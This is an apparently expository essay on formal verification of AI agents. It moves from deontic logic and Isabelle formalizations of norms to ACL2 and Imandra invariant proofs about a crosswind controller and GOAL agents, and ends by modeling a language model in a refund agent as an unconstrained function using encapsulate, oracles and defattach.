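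The Stanford Encyclopedia of Philosophy's *A Bit More on Chisholm's Paradox* traces the contradiction to two ways of getting an unconditional obligation from a conditional one. *Deontic detachment* combines "if Jones goes, he ought to tell his neighbours he is coming" with "Jones ought to go". *Factual detachment* combines "if Jones stays at home, he ought not to tell them" with the fact that he stays at home. System E avoids the contradiction by allowing the first and blocking the second, although people make the second inference all the time. It therefore proves that Jones ought to tell his neighbours he is coming, even though he isn't, and does not prove that he ought not to tell them. An agent that has already failed at something needs to derive the obligation that applies after the failure, rather than the one that assumed it would succeed.

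According to the Stanford Encyclopedia of Philosophy's *Supplement to Deontic Logic*, the central challenge for such logics is to explain the point of conditional obligations that nobody can ever detach from their conditions. Many of their defenders allow factual detachment when the condition is settled, meaning it is too late to change. José Carmo and Andrew Jones built a logic on this idea with separate operators for what ideally ought to happen and what actually ought to happen, given what the agent has decided. In the promise example, you ideally ought to keep your promise and not apologize, but actually ought to apologize. The Internet Encyclopedia of Philosophy objects that "ought" doesn't seem to have two meanings here, and that nobody can act on both obligations at once. An engineer would have to choose one to control the agent, presumably the actual obligation.

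A different approach treats norms as defaults, which apply unless something defeats them. *A logic for default deontic reasoning* (2025) argues that a reasoner who accepts an obligation only when nothing could override it will accept too few.

### From ethical robots to LogiKEy

*Toward Ethical Robots via Mechanized Deontic Logic* (Konstantine Arkoudas, Selmer Bringsjord and Paul Bello, AAAI symposium, 2005) proposes using machine-checked proofs in deontic logic to establish that a robot's actions are permissible or obligatory. An English translation of the proof could then explain the robot's reasons. The paper encodes a deontic logic in the proof system Athena and works through an example. *Toward a General Logicist Methodology for Engineering Ethically Correct Robots* (Bringsjord, Arkoudas and Bello, 2006) argues that a robot should perform only actions that it can prove permissible in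 a logic that people have chosen.

That design is cautious as long as the norms are consistent. If they are inconsistent, every statement follows from them, so the robot can prove any action permissible. A designer therefore has to check the norms and the logic before the robot uses them.

*Designing Normative Theories for Ethical and Legal Reasoning* (Benzmüller, Parent and van der Torre, 2019) presents LogiKEy, a method for formalizing rules that state obligations. Its three layers are a logic, a set of norms written in that logic, and an application that uses the norms. If a check fails at one layer, the developer can revise any of the others, including the logic.

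A LogiKEy developer doesn't write a new prover for each deontic logic. The developer defines the logic inside Isabelle/HOL, where a sentence becomes a function that takes a world and returns true or false. The operators are then ordinary definitions:

```
(O p) at w     =  for every world v acceptable from w:  p at v
O(q/p) at w    =  for every best world v among the p-worlds:  q at v
```

System E takes about 30 lines to define in Isabelle. Isabelle's tools then work on the new logic, including its automatic provers and Nitpick. Nitpick is a *model finder*, which searches for a small set of worlds in which given sentences are all true. A proof on paper shows that a formula is valid in system E exactly when its translation is valid in Isabelle's logic. ACL2 has no variables for functions, so an ACL2 user would have to store formulas as lists and write a function that evaluates them at each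 world.

Benzmüller and colleagues tested the method on a small case from the European Union's data protection regulation:

1. A company must process personal data lawfully.
2. If it has processed data unlawfully, it must erase them.
3. It must keep data that it has processed lawfully (an obligation from an agreement with the customer, outside the regulation).
4. It has processed the data of a customer, Peter, unlawfully.

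In standard deontic logic, Nitpick found no model of these sentences, and one of Isabelle's provers derived a contradiction from them within a few milliseconds. Isabelle then proved that the company must erase Peter's data, that it must keep them, and that someone ought to kill Mary, whom none of the norms mention. In system E, Nitpick found a model of the norms and a countermodel to the claim that someone ought to kill Mary.

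The first of these two results is weaker than it looks. System E places no conditions on the ranking of worlds, so a model may have no best worlds, which makes every conditional obligation trivially true. Even "erase the data" and "do not erase the data", under the same condition, are both true in such a model. The countermodel is better evidence, because "someone ought to kill Mary" is false only if there is a best world in which nobody kills her. A developer can exclude the trivial models by requiring a best world for every condition that can occur.

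The norms also have an awkward consequence for the company. System E proves an unconditional obligation to keep Peter's data, because in the best worlds the company has processed the data lawfully and keeps them. The company can derive the obligation to erase them only by asking what it ought to do given that the processing was unlawful.

A consistent set of norms can still be bad. If the second norm required the company to keep unlawfully processed data, the set would still be consistent, and every condition would still have a best world. An inconsistency is a more definite finding than consistency, and people can overlook one for decades. The 2026 teaching paper by Benzmüller and colleagues recounts how an automatic prover found that Kurt Gödel's original axioms for the existence of God contradict each other.

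Failing to find a model is less conclusive, because Nitpick searches only finite models. One student tried without success to use it on a logic of action and time, because that logic requires infinite models.

The choice of logic also matters when a language model writes the formulas. Farjami and colleagues tested GPT-4o and DeepSeek-V1 on 103 short arguments, 47 of them typical of bioethics, and used Isabelle to check whether each argument's explanation proved its conclusion. If the proof failed, the language model could revise the explanation up to three times. GPT-4o with standard deontic logic had the highest success rate, 77.67%. First-order logic validated fewer explanations overall but did best on common-sense reasoning, while the logics of conditional obligation led to more syntax errors. Standard deontic logic thus came first even though it fails on Chisholm's sentences, perhaps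 partly because its formulas are easier to write. Both language models are far behind those of late 2026, so the success rates are a poor guide to current systems. A success also means only that the conclusion follows from the explanation, which a language model can achieve by adding a doubtful premise.

### Gewirth's argument in Isabelle

Fuenmayor and Benzmüller (2019), in *Harnessing Higher-Order (Meta-)Logic to Represent and Reason with Complex Ethical Theories*, applied the method to a full philosophical argument. Alan Gewirth claimed that anyone who acts for a purpose must, to avoid contradicting themselves, accept that every such agent has a right to freedom and well-being. In outline:

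1. I act for some purpose, so I am an agent.
2. I regard that purpose as good.
3. I need freedom and well-being to achieve any purpose at all.
4. My freedom and well-being are therefore necessary goods for me.
5. I therefore have a right to them.
6. The same reasoning applies to every agent, so every agent has this right.

The formalization uses Carmo and Jones's logic, extended to handle words like "I", whose reference depends on the speaker. It defines a right to something as an ideal obligation that nobody interfere with it.

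The prover did not accept the argument as Gewirth gave it. Fuenmayor and Benzmüller had to add or change three premises, mostly to get from step 4 to step 5:

- If something is necessarily good from an agent's perspective, and it is possible, then it ought to be.
- If something ought to be, then it ought to be possible. (Gewirth's argument relied on the more familiar "ought implies can".)
- Someone interferes with a state of affairs if and only if that state is not actually possible.

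With these premises, Isabelle checks the whole proof in under a second on an ordinary laptop. It also confirms that the last step, which generalizes from "I" to everyone, needs no further moral principle, as long as necessity has the speaker-dependent sense used in the formalization.

Fuenmayor and Benzmüller call the problems they fixed minor, but the first premise turns what is good for a person into an obligation, and the definition of a right turns that obligation into a demand on other people. Anyone who doubts that one person's needs create duties for others can now point to the exact lines they reject. The third premise is also doubtful, because it implies that whenever a person's well-being is impossible, someone is interfering with it, even if the cause is an incurable illness. Isabelle can't detect this problem, because the premise is consistent with the others.

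Nitpick showed that the axioms are consistent by finding a model with two worlds and one individual. Because the model has only one individual, it can't show what happens when one agent's freedom threatens another's well-being, which is where an agent would most need guidance.

The formalization of Gewirth's principle barely defines "freedom and well-being". Its axioms state only that agents need it for every purpose, can have it and can lack it. The theorem therefore holds for any property that meets these conditions, probably including being alive, just as a theorem about a constrained function in ACL2 holds for any function that satisfies the constraints. Kornai proposed in 2014 that the principle could keep an artificial general intelligence from violating human rights. A machine built that way would still need some method beyond the theorem to recognize which beings are agents and which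 of its actions interfere with their freedom.

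## Proving that an agent stays safe over every possible run

The checks on the refund rules concern a single decision, but an agent makes many decisions, and each can depend on earlier ones. For example, each payment the refund agent makes counts toward its daily limit of 500, which affects how it handles later requests. There are infinitely many possible sequences of requests, so they can't be checked one by one. Two facts are enough to prove that the agent stays within the limit in all of them. First, the day's total starts at 0. Second, if the total is at most 500 before a request, it is at most 500 afterwards, because the agent pays only if the new total would be within the limit, and a refusal leaves the total unchanged. The total therefore never exceeds 500, however many requests arrive.

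### Proof by invariant

The same argument works for any agent whose next state depends only on its current state and the next input. The developer chooses a set of "good" states and proves three things:

1. The start state is good.
2. From a good state, every input that can occur leads to another good state.
3. Every good state is safe.

Being good is then an invariant, and the agent is safe throughout every run. In ACL2, a function can run the agent on a list of inputs:

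```
(defun run (s inputs)
  (if (endp inputs)
      s
    (run (next-state s (car inputs)) (cdr inputs))))

(defthm run-stays-good
  (implies (and (good s) (all-allowed inputs))
           (good (run s inputs))))
```

Here all-allowed is true if every item on the list is an input that can occur. The proof is by induction on the list. Condition 2 shows that the state after the first input is good, and the induction hypothesis covers the rest of the list from that state. As with the toy machine, proving the theorem for every finite run also proves it for every moment of an endless run.

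For the refund agent, the good states are the safe ones. More often, though, a safe state can lead to an unsafe one. A car in the middle of its lane is safe, but if it is moving sideways at speed, it will soon be unsafe. In such cases the developer has to find a narrower set of good states, which usually takes more thought than the induction.

### A vehicle in a crosswind

A steering program that keeps a car on the road in a breeze might fail in a storm, so a proof about an agent that acts on the world needs a model of the world as well. Boyer, Green and Moore built such a model in the early 1980s in *The use of a formal simulator to verify a simple real time control program*. They defined one mathematical function for the program and its environment together, and used ACL2's predecessor, the Boyer–Moore prover, to show that a vehicle keeps to a straight course in a changing crosswind. Imandra's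 documentation repeats the proof.

The intended course is a straight line, and the model tracks only sideways movement, in whole units. Its state has three parts:

- w is the wind speed, measured as the distance the wind would blow a passive vehicle in one interval.
- y is the vehicle's distance from the line, negative on one side and positive on the other.
- v is the sideways speed that the controller has built up so far.

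In each interval the wind speed changes by d, which is −1, 0 or 1. The wind may still become arbitrarily strong, as long as it does so gradually. With sgn(y) for the sign of y (−1, 0 or 1), the new values are:

```
w' = w + d
y' = y + v + w + d
v' = v − 3·sgn(y') + 2·sgn(y)
```

The last line is the controller. It uses only the side of the line that the vehicle is on now and the side it was on one interval ago. If the vehicle is still on the same side, the controller changes v by 1 towards the line. If the vehicle has just left the line, the controller changes v by 3 back towards it. If the vehicle has crossed the line, the controller changes v by 5 against the vehicle's motion. If the vehicle has just reached the line, the controller changes v by 2 to slow it down.

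The definition of a good state must be stricter than "at most 3 units from the line". If y is 3 and v + w is 5, the vehicle is within that limit, but in the next interval it will be at least 7 units away. An attempt to prove condition 2 with the looser definition fails and may produce that state as a counterexample. The counterexample doesn't reveal a fault in the controller, because a vehicle that starts at rest on the line never reaches that state.

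A better definition has to deal with w and v, both of which can grow without limit. Only their sum matters, however. The new position depends on y, w + v and d, and so does the new value of w + v. This sum is the distance the vehicle will drift in the next interval if the wind doesn't change. The good states are those with one of 13 combinations of position and drift:

| Position y | Drift w + v |
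|---|---|
| −3 | 1 |
| −2 | 1 or 2 |
| −1 | 2 or 3 |
| 0 | −1, 0 or 1 |
| 1 | −2 or −3 |
| 2 | −1 or −2 |
| 3 | −1 |

Whenever the vehicle is off the line, its drift points back towards the line. With 13 pairs on the list and three possible changes in the wind, condition 2 has 13 × 3 = 39 cases. For example, if the wind changes by 1 at the pair (−1, 3), the new position is −1 + 3 + 1 = 3. The vehicle has crossed the line, so the controller subtracts 5, and the new drift is 3 + 1 − 5 = −1. The resulting pair, (3, −1), is on the list, as are (2, −2) and (1, −3), which result from the other two changes.

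Imandra first proves the single-step theorem. The notebook then switches off the definitions of the step function and of a good state, so that during the induction over whole runs Imandra uses the theorem as a rule instead of working through the cases again at every step. This proves that a vehicle starting at (0, 0, 0) never gets more than 3 units from the line under any possible history of the wind.

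A model checker could have found the 13 pairs mechanically, by starting from (0, 0) and adding every pair that can follow until the list stopped growing. Every pair on the list can occur, so no smaller set would work. For example, wind changes of 1, 0 and 1 take the vehicle to position 3. The search would never finish on the original triples, because the wind can always reach a new speed. It finishes on the pairs because w and v matter only through their sum, so one number can replace both, leaving only 13 reachable states.

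### Returning to the line

A controller could satisfy the first theorem by holding the vehicle 2 units from the line forever. The second theorem rules this out. If the wind stays constant for at least four intervals, the vehicle returns to the line and stays there until the wind changes. This sets a deadline for the return instead of requiring only that it happen eventually.

Four is the smallest number for which the theorem holds. Suppose the wind changes by 1 twice and then stays constant. The vehicle's positions are 1 and 0 during the changes, then 1, −1, 2 and 0 while the wind is constant. The vehicle is on the line but drifting when the wind settles, and the controller makes it overshoot to each side before it comes to rest.

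The Imandra notebook proves two versions of this. The one it presents as the final result proves almost nothing, because it starts the vehicle at (0, 0, 0) and assumes that the wind never changes, so nothing pushes the vehicle off the line. The useful version is the lemma just before it, which starts from any good state. Together with the theorem that every run stays among the good states, this lemma covers a wind that blows in any permitted way and then becomes steady. A prover accepts both versions, so a reader has to check a theorem's assumptions as well as its title.

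### A faulty controller and a false assumption

To show how the method catches mistakes, Imandra's notebook also tries to prove the 3-unit limit for a flawed controller. The proof fails, and Imandra returns a counterexample in which the wind changes by 1 three times in a row. Replacing −3 with −4 in the control rule is enough to cause this failure. The table compares it with runs of the correct rule:

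| Controller | Changes in the wind | Positions |
|---|---|---|
| correct | 1, 1, 1 | 1, 0, 2 |
| correct | 1, 0, 1 | 1, −1, 3 |
| flawed (−4 instead of −3) | 1, 1, 1 | 1, −1, 4 |
| correct | 1, 0, 2 | 1, −1, 4 |

In the last row the controller is correct, but the wind changes by 2 in a single interval, and the model assumes it changes by at most 1. The vehicle ends up in the same place as with the flawed controller. If the road is 3 units wide on each side, the vehicle is off the road, even though the theorem is still true. No prover could have detected this, because the theorem covers only winds that stay within the model's limit.

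If the wind stays constant after the gust, the vehicle's next positions are 4, 3, 1, −2 and 0, so it recovers one interval later than the second theorem would have required. If the wind keeps rising by 2 per interval, the positions are 6, 9, 13 and so on without limit. While the vehicle stays on one side of the line, the controller corrects its speed by only 1 per interval, which exactly offsets a wind that rises by 1 but is too small for one that rises by 2. A larger set of good states wouldn't fix this, so handling stronger gusts requires a different controller.

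Assumptions can also be too favorable to the agent in less obvious ways. Suppose the developer had described the wind as "changing by at most 1 per interval and never blowing the vehicle more than 3 units off course". A controller that does nothing would then be provably safe, because the assumed wind always adjusts to keep the vehicle within 3 units of its course. The assumptions about an environment should therefore describe what it can do regardless of what the agent does.

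The equations contain other simplifications. They place no limit on how fast v can change, and the controller sometimes demands a change of 5 units within one interval, which a heavy vehicle might not manage. They also assume that the sensor never reports the wrong side of the line and that the correction always takes effect before the next interval. Boyer and Moore (1983), in *Proof-Checking, Theorem-Proving, and Program Verification*, called the crosswind proof a "minor investigation" and identified timing, interrupts and specifying the real world as major problems in verifying such controllers.

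Later tools have removed some of these simplifications. For example, *Verification of Autonomous Neural Car Control with KeYmaera X* (Prebet, Teuber and Platzer, 2025) uses a model that includes continuous motion to prove that a car with a neural-network controller avoids collisions on trips of any length.

### Agents with beliefs and goals

Many researchers prefer to program autonomous agents in terms of what the agents believe and want. GOAL is a programming language for doing this. In *Machine-checked Verification of Cognitive Agents*, Jensen (2022) put a complete method for proving properties of GOAL agents into Isabelle/HOL, based on a theory that de Boer, Hindriks and colleagues published in 2007.

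A GOAL agent's state is a *mental state*, which consists of a list of beliefs and a list of goals. Both are formulas of propositional logic, built from yes-or-no facts with "and", "or" and "not". The beliefs must be consistent, each goal must be logically possible, and the agent can't have a goal that it already believes it has achieved. Two operators query the mental state:

- Bφ means that φ follows from the agent's beliefs.
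- Gφ means that φ follows from one of its goals and that the agent doesn't yet believe φ.

*Towards Verifying GOAL Agents in Isabelle/HOL*, by Jensen, gives the example of an agent that wants to be at home and watch a movie, and so also has the goal of being at home. But an agent with two separate goals need not have the goal of achieving both together. It can want to be in Paris and also want to be in London, as long as it doesn't want to be in both at the same time.

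The agent acts through *conditional actions*, each pairing an action with a condition on the agent's mental state. The agent can carry out the action only when the condition is true. The action then changes the agent's beliefs, and the agent deletes any goal it now believes it has achieved. One built-in action adopts a goal, and another drops one.

To describe the effect of an action, Jensen uses *Hoare triples*. The triple {φ} a {ψ} means that if φ is true before action a, then ψ is true after it. The developer supplies some triples as axioms about the particular agent. *Effect axioms* describe what an action changes, and *frame axioms* describe what it leaves alone. Further triples follow from general rules, such as:

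- A goal remains a goal or becomes a belief, unless the agent drops it.
- If φ implies that the agent cannot carry out a, then {φ} a {φ}.
- To prove {φ} b {χ} for a conditional action b with action a and condition ψ, prove {φ and ψ} a {χ}, and also prove that χ is already true whenever φ is true and ψ is false.

A developer could write effect axioms that contradict each other, as with the refund axioms earlier. The method therefore requires a proof that some way of updating the beliefs satisfies them all. ACL2's encapsulate command similarly requires an example function.

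An invariant proof for a GOAL agent is similar to the one for the vehicle. If φ is true at the start and {φ} b {φ} holds for every conditional action b, then φ is true throughout every run. Jensen proved in Isabelle that checking each action separately is enough. The vehicle proof instead needed a check for every combination of a good pair and a change in the wind.

Proving liveness takes more than proving safety. To prove that φ leads to ψ in one stage, the developer shows that every action either keeps φ true or makes ψ true, and that at least one action is certain to make ψ true. This still doesn't guarantee that the agent ever selects that action, so Jensen assumes *fairness*, meaning that the agent tries every action again and again. An action whose condition is false does nothing, so without fairness the agent could keep trying such an action forever and the theorem would be false.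 The developer can then chain several such stages together. Russinoff (1992), in *A Verification System for Concurrent Programs*, had earlier added rules for both safety and liveness to the Boyer–Moore prover and used them on a program in which two processes compute binomial coefficients.

### What Jensen verified

Jensen's example is an agent that fetches a block. It starts in a "dropzone" with the goal "collect" and has five actions:

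| Action | Condition (what the agent believes) | Effect on its beliefs |
|---|---|---|
| go-room | in the dropzone, not holding a block | in the room |
| go-block | in the room, not at the block, not holding it | at the block |
| pick-up | at the block, not holding it | holding the block |
| go-dropzone | in the room, holding the block | in the dropzone |
| put-down | in the dropzone, holding the block | block collected |

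The theorem is that the agent eventually believes it has collected the block. The proof is a chain of five stages, one for each action. In the third stage, the agent is next to the block, and the action pick-up makes "holding" true. Each of the other four actions must leave the situation unchanged, and for go-room this depends on an invariant. Go-room requires the agent to believe it is in the dropzone, so the developer must rule out that an agent in the room also believes this.

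The general framework takes about 2,400 lines of Isabelle. The example takes another 1,100, or more than 200 for each of its five actions. Jensen simplified the example from a real GOAL program and, working outside Isabelle, translated it into the logic. Only one action can do anything in each state, so the proof involves no choice between actions. Jensen says such proofs are tedious to do by hand and that Isabelle's automation is poorly suited to them. That may be less of an obstacle now that coding agents can write long proofs in other provers.

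The more serious limitation is that the model assumes only the agent's own actions change anything, and that every action has its stated effect. Nobody else can move the block, and the gripper never slips. The final theorem concerns the agent's beliefs, and an agent whose gripper has slipped may believe it has delivered a block that is still lying in the room. If the model included such failures, the theorem as stated would be false. *On using Theorem Proving for Cognitive Agent-oriented Programming* (Jensen, Hindriks and Villadsen, 2021) cites work by Winikoff for the point that "the agent will eventually succeed" is too strong to prove when actions can fail. A developer would have to prove something weaker, for example that the agent succeeds if the gripper works at least once in every ten attempts, or that it never reports a delivery without checking the dropzone.

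The framework also handles only one agent at a time. Propositional logic cannot refer to "any room" or "any block", so describing a building with fifty rooms requires a separate fact for each room.

### Model checking the same kind of agent

Most verification of agents with beliefs and goals uses model checking rather than theorem proving. *Model checking agent programming languages* (Dennis, Fisher and colleagues, 2011) presents a system that works for many agent languages. A toolkit of Java classes helps developers write an interpreter for each language. The agent program runs in this interpreter, which notifies a model checker called Agent Java PathFinder whenever the agent reaches a relevant new state. The model checker then checks whether every possible execution satisfies the required property.

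The properties can refer to an agent's beliefs, goals and intentions, so a developer can check why the agent acts as well as what it does. For example, a developer might require that a warehouse robot never enter an aisle unless it believes the aisle is empty. A robot that enters without checking violates this requirement even if the aisle is empty every time. The system can also check a group of agents written in different languages, which Jensen's framework cannot do.

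Dennis and colleagues chose model checking because it is automatic, whereas theorem proving usually needs an expert and is often very costly. They acknowledged that their system was relatively slow, especially with more agents. Such agents' programs have many possible paths, and adding code to handle failures increases the number considerably, according to research that Jensen and colleagues cite. Developers often add assumptions to reduce the number of states, but each assumption narrows what the result covers.

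Model checking is clearly the better choice for the block agent because a program could explore its handful of facts and one possible action at a time almost instantly. Any GOAL agent with a fixed list of yes-or-no facts has only finitely many mental states that differ in meaning, so exhaustive exploration could in principle settle every question that Jensen's framework can express about it. Jensen and colleagues argue that theorem proving suits agent programs because they are short and use high-level concepts. The block agent doesn't yet support this argument, since its proof is far longer than its program. A theorem prover would have the advantage for agents whose state includes unlimited quantities or lists, such as the vehicle's wind speed or the refund agent's payment history.

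Both methods have difficulty with the environment. Jensen and colleagues judged debugging, automated testing and model checking to be well established for beliefs, decision rules and groups of agents, but only debugging to be well established for the environment. They put a question mark against theorem proving in every row of their comparison table.

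## Treating the learned model as an unknown function

The crosswind proof covers every permitted wind, so it needs no theory of the weather. A developer can treat a language model inside an agent in much the same way. Nobody has a usable definition of the model, but a theorem that holds for every function that could replace the model also holds for the model itself. This works only if the model behaves like a function, which takes some care to arrange.

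### The model proposes and the rules decide

Suppose the shop adds a language model to its refund agent. The model reads the customer's message, judges whether the complaint is genuine and proposes a decision. In ACL2, the developer declares a function called propose and leaves it undefined:

```
(defstub propose (* * * *) => *)

(defun act (message verified flagged amount)
  (if (equal (propose message verified flagged amount) 'approve)
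      (decide verified flagged amount)
    'refuse))
```

The stars stand for four arguments and one result. If the model proposes approval, the repaired refund rules in decide settle the matter. Otherwise the agent refuses. ACL2 can prove that every approved refund satisfies the rules:

```
(thm (implies (equal (act message verified flagged amount) 'approve)
              (and verified
                   (not flagged)
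                   (<= amount 100))))
```

The proof has two cases. If propose returns approve, then act returns whatever decide returns, and ACL2 goes through the lines of decide as before. If propose returns anything else, act returns refuse, which contradicts the assumption. Neither case depends on how propose computes its answer, so the theorem covers a good model, a bad one, and one that a customer has manipulated through the message. The shop can also switch to a newer model without a new proof.

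The converse would be that every entitled customer gets a refund:

```
(thm (implies (and verified (not flagged) (<= amount 100))
              (equal (act message verified flagged amount) 'approve)))
```

This proof fails. ACL2 reduces the formula to the claim that propose returns approve, but it has no facts about propose. The claim is false for some functions, such as the one that always returns refuse.

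### Constraints and witnesses

To prove the converse, the developer has to assume something about the model. The encapsulate command can replace the defstub line and state the assumption:

```
(encapsulate
  (((propose * * * *) => *))
  (local (defun propose (message verified flagged amount)
           (declare (ignore message verified flagged amount))
           'approve))
  (defthm proposes-for-entitled
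    (implies (and verified (not flagged) (<= amount 100))
             (equal (propose message verified flagged amount)
                    'approve))))
```

The local definition is the example function that encapsulate requires, called a *witness*. As ACL2's *Encapsulate* explains, ACL2 processes the command twice. On the first pass it admits the witness and proves the theorem. It then rolls everything back, and on the second pass it keeps only the function's name, its number of arguments and the theorem, which becomes a constraint. The constraint cannot make the logic inconsistent, because the witness satisfies it. This witness approves everything, so it would be useless as a model, but that doesn't affect later proofs because they can't use its definition.

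With the constraint, ACL2 proves the converse, but only for models that propose approval for every entitled customer. Nobody has shown that the shop's model does this.

*Functional instantiation* applies a theorem about a constrained function to a specific function. In ACL2's *A small proof demonstrating functional instantiation*, the constrained function is an operation that is associative and commutative and has an identity element, with addition as the witness. ACL2 proves that combining the items of a list with this operation gives the same result if the list is reversed first. The user then substitutes multiplication, with 1 as the identity. Once ACL2 has checked that multiplication satisfies the constraints, the theorem about products follows without another induction. In a much larger example, from the 2025 workshop proceedings edited by Gamboa and Manolios, David Russinoff proves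 the main facts about determinants over any commutative ring.

If the shop replaced its language model with a keyword search written in ACL2, the safety theorem would still hold without further proof, because it needs no constraint on propose. The converse would require a proof that the keyword search proposes approval for every entitled customer.

A developer who defines act inside encapsulate can constrain propose by accident. If the witness always refuses, ACL2 can use it to prove that act never approves a refund. That theorem becomes a constraint on propose, and most models violate it. ACL2 requires anyone who substitutes another function for propose to prove this constraint too. ACL2's manual shows that a looser rule, which counted only the theorems that mention the constrained function directly, would be unsound. Under that rule, a user could start with a witness that returns x unchanged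 and end with a proof that (cons x x) equals x. ACL2 prints the constraints when it accepts the encapsulate command, so a reader can check them.

### Which guarantees need an assumption about the model

| Statement about the refund agent | What it requires of the model |
|---|---|
| Every approved refund satisfies the rules. | nothing |
| The day's refunds never exceed 500. | nothing |
| Every entitled customer gets a refund. | It proposes approval for all of them. |
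| Nobody gets a refund for an invented complaint. | It recognizes invented complaints. |

The surrounding code can enforce the first two statements by refusing, which never violates either. Refusing can't enforce the third, and it would enforce the fourth only if the code refused everyone. This division is slightly different from the one between safety and liveness. "The agent never refuses an entitled customer" is a safety property, since the record of a single refusal can violate it, yet it depends on the model. The code can enforce a statement if it always has an acceptable action available, whatever the model proposes. Doing nothing is not acceptable for a moving car, so the code needs a safe manoeuvre of its own.

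A developer can recover some usefulness without trusting the model. If the last line of act returns escalate instead of refuse, ACL2 can prove that every entitled customer either gets a refund or reaches an employee. This theorem also holds if the model never proposes approval, in which case the agent sends every request to an employee. Removing propose from act would make the full converse true, but the agent would then pay refunds for invented complaints. The shop added the model to make a judgement that the rules don't express, and nobody can prove that judgement correct without a formal statement of what makes a complaint genuine.

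In *Containment Verification*, Moon and Varshney (2026) apply the same idea to PocketFlow, a small framework for building agents. They represent the AI as a method with no body in Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier, so the verifier must allow for every action that the method's declared type permits. The proof establishes that the agent reads files only inside its workspace, calls only tools on an approved list and takes no more than a fixed number of steps. A more capable model can't break these limits through the verified code, because the theorem covers every sequence of actions.

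That guarantee weakens as the permitted actions get broader. If one of them were "run this shell command", a model could do almost anything in a single permitted step. Moon and Varshney also assume that every outside effect passes through the verified code, and they exclude properties of content, such as truthfulness.

*Lean4Agent* aims to prove that each step of a workflow receives what it needs from earlier steps, which is closer to proving that the workflow is useful. Its proofs rest on an assumption, called LLMExec, that the language model can produce output that meets a step's requirements when given suitable input. The software then checks actual runs against those requirements, partly with another language model as a judge. On two benchmarks, workflows that passed the formal check outperformed those that failed it by 11.94% on average, so the check seems to identify better workflows.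 But the proofs don't show how often the model will produce output that meets the requirements.

Nguyen's experiment in *VerAct* shows that agents can be kept within their constraints and still fail at their tasks. In 28,080 episodes with four language models, a symbolic check on each proposed action let through no constraint violations, and the agents succeeded in 80.1% of episodes. A correct check would let through no violations with any model, but the success rate was measured only for those models on those tasks.

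### When the same question gets different answers

A language model usually chooses each word partly at random, so it may answer the same question differently each time, which a function in ACL2's logic cannot do. Suppose the developer has the agent ask the model twice and escalate if the answers differ. With propose as defined above, ACL2 can prove that this escalation never happens, since both calls have the same arguments. The theorem is correct for every function of those four arguments, but the model's answer also depends on the random choices, so the real system can escalate.

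Setting the model's "temperature" to zero turns off the random choice but does not solve this. Thinking Machines Lab's *Defeating Nondeterminism in LLM Inference* notes that the answers of commercial language models still vary at that setting. One cause, according to *The Token Not Taken* (2026), is that servers process several users' requests together, and the size of the group can change the order in which they add numbers. Computer arithmetic rounds, so the order affects the result. *Same Request, Different Answer* (2026) excluded that cause by sending requests one at a time, and attributed the remaining variation to the reuse of stored calculations. With this reuse switched off, the answers repeated exactly.

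ACL2 users had already met this problem when modeling system calls. In *Modeling nondeterminism inherent in y86 system calls*, Kaufmann (2013) wanted to model a processor whose programs call the operating system. The result of writing to a file depends on more than the call's arguments, so Kaufmann first tried adding a clock reading as an extra argument, with a different reading for each call. But two ACL2 sessions could get different results for the same reading, and each could save a theorem recording its result. Anyone who loaded both theorems could then prove a contradiction.

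The solution was an *oracle*, a list in the machine's state that holds the results of all future outside calls. Each call takes the next result from the list. The operating system supplies the results when the program runs, so nobody has to build the list. A theorem about every possible oracle applies to that run, since one of those oracles contains the results that occurred. In Kaufmann's demonstration, writing "hello" returns 6, but an attempt to prove that it returns 6 fails, as it should. The oracle may also contain impossible results, such as data from a file that the program never opened. A safety theorem that covers every oracle still holds for the real results, but the impossible ones can make a true statement unprovable.

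ACL2 treats random numbers in the same way. According to ACL2's *Random$*, the expression (random$ 10 state) takes the next item from an oracle that ACL2 has no facts about. If the item is not a whole number from 0 to 9, the result is 0. ACL2 can therefore prove that the result is always in range, but not that the ten results are about equally likely, because the logical definition contains no probabilities.

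For the refund agent, the oracle is a list of the model's replies. In the function run from the previous section, each input becomes a request paired with a reply. The proof that the agent stays within its daily limit works as before, except that the single-step theorem must now cover every reply to every request. The list may contain different replies to the same request, so the proof also covers a model that samples its replies. A real model chooses each reply after seeing what has happened so far, but the proof still applies because some list contains those replies in that order. The developer can replace a malformed reply with refuse, just as random$ replaces an item out of range.

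*Provably Auditable and Safe LLM Agents from Human-Authored Ontologies* (Sterling, 2026) uses an oracle for systems with several agents. Suppose two agents share a budget of $100,000, and one wants to spend $45,000 and the other $60,000. Each amount is within the budget, but the total exceeds it, so agents that act independently may overspend. In Sterling's design, agents only make proposals, and a central checker that sees the whole state decides which to carry out. Sterling's main theorem is that if the invariants hold at the start, they hold in every state the system can reach, whatever the language models and tools reply. Sterling leaves liveness to another paper.

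### Running the real model

ACL2 cannot run a constrained function, because it has no definition to compute with. The defattach command lets another function run in its place:

```
(defattach propose keyword-propose)
```

ACL2 first proves that keyword-propose satisfies the constraints on propose and that the guard of keyword-propose allows every argument that the guard of propose allows. It also rejects circular attachments. Without that check, a user could attach to f a function that calls f and returns the opposite result, and running f would never end.

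An attachment lets ACL2 run an unconstrained function but doesn't affect proofs about it. In an example from ACL2's *Defattach*, a user attaches a function that adds 3 to an unconstrained function `f`. Typing `(f 2)` then gives 5, but the prover can't replace `(f 2)` with 5 because no axiom about `f` justifies it. Theorems about `propose` therefore still hold for every possible model after the developer chooses one to run.

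A neural network is harder to attach, because the agent reaches it through a call to an outside program. Suppose the model also reads the amount from a photograph of the receipt, and the developer adds the constraint that this amount is correct. The developer can't prove that the network satisfies the constraint, because ACL2 has no definition of the network. Translating the network's weights into ACL2 wouldn't be enough, because the proof would also need a formal definition of the amount that a photograph shows.

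The `:skip-checks` option permits the attachment anyway, but ACL2 then requires a trust tag, which marks the result as dependent on unverified code. The manual says of this case, "We do not make any logical claims."

It is usually better to change the program so that it doesn't need the constraint. If the shop's records contain the price of each purchase, the code can reject any refund above that price. A misread receipt may then make a refund too small, but it can't push the refund above the price. For the proposals, it is simplest to keep the model outside ACL2. An ordinary program calls the model and passes the reply to the function `act` as an argument. The developer then doesn't need an attachment, and a theorem about every possible reply covers whatever the model returns.

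Sometimes a proof needs the results of outside code. *Partial-encapsulate and Its Support for Floating-point Operations in ACL2* (Kaufmann and Moore, 2025) describes a command for this purpose, which ACL2 has had since 2019 but few people have used. A function introduced with partial-encapsulate has unstated constraints in addition to the stated ones. Typically, every result that anyone will ever compute with the function counts as an axiom. In the demonstration *partial-encapsulate.lisp* (Kaufmann, 2018), ACL2 runs outside code to prove that its approximation of the natural logarithm of 3 equals 1.0986123.

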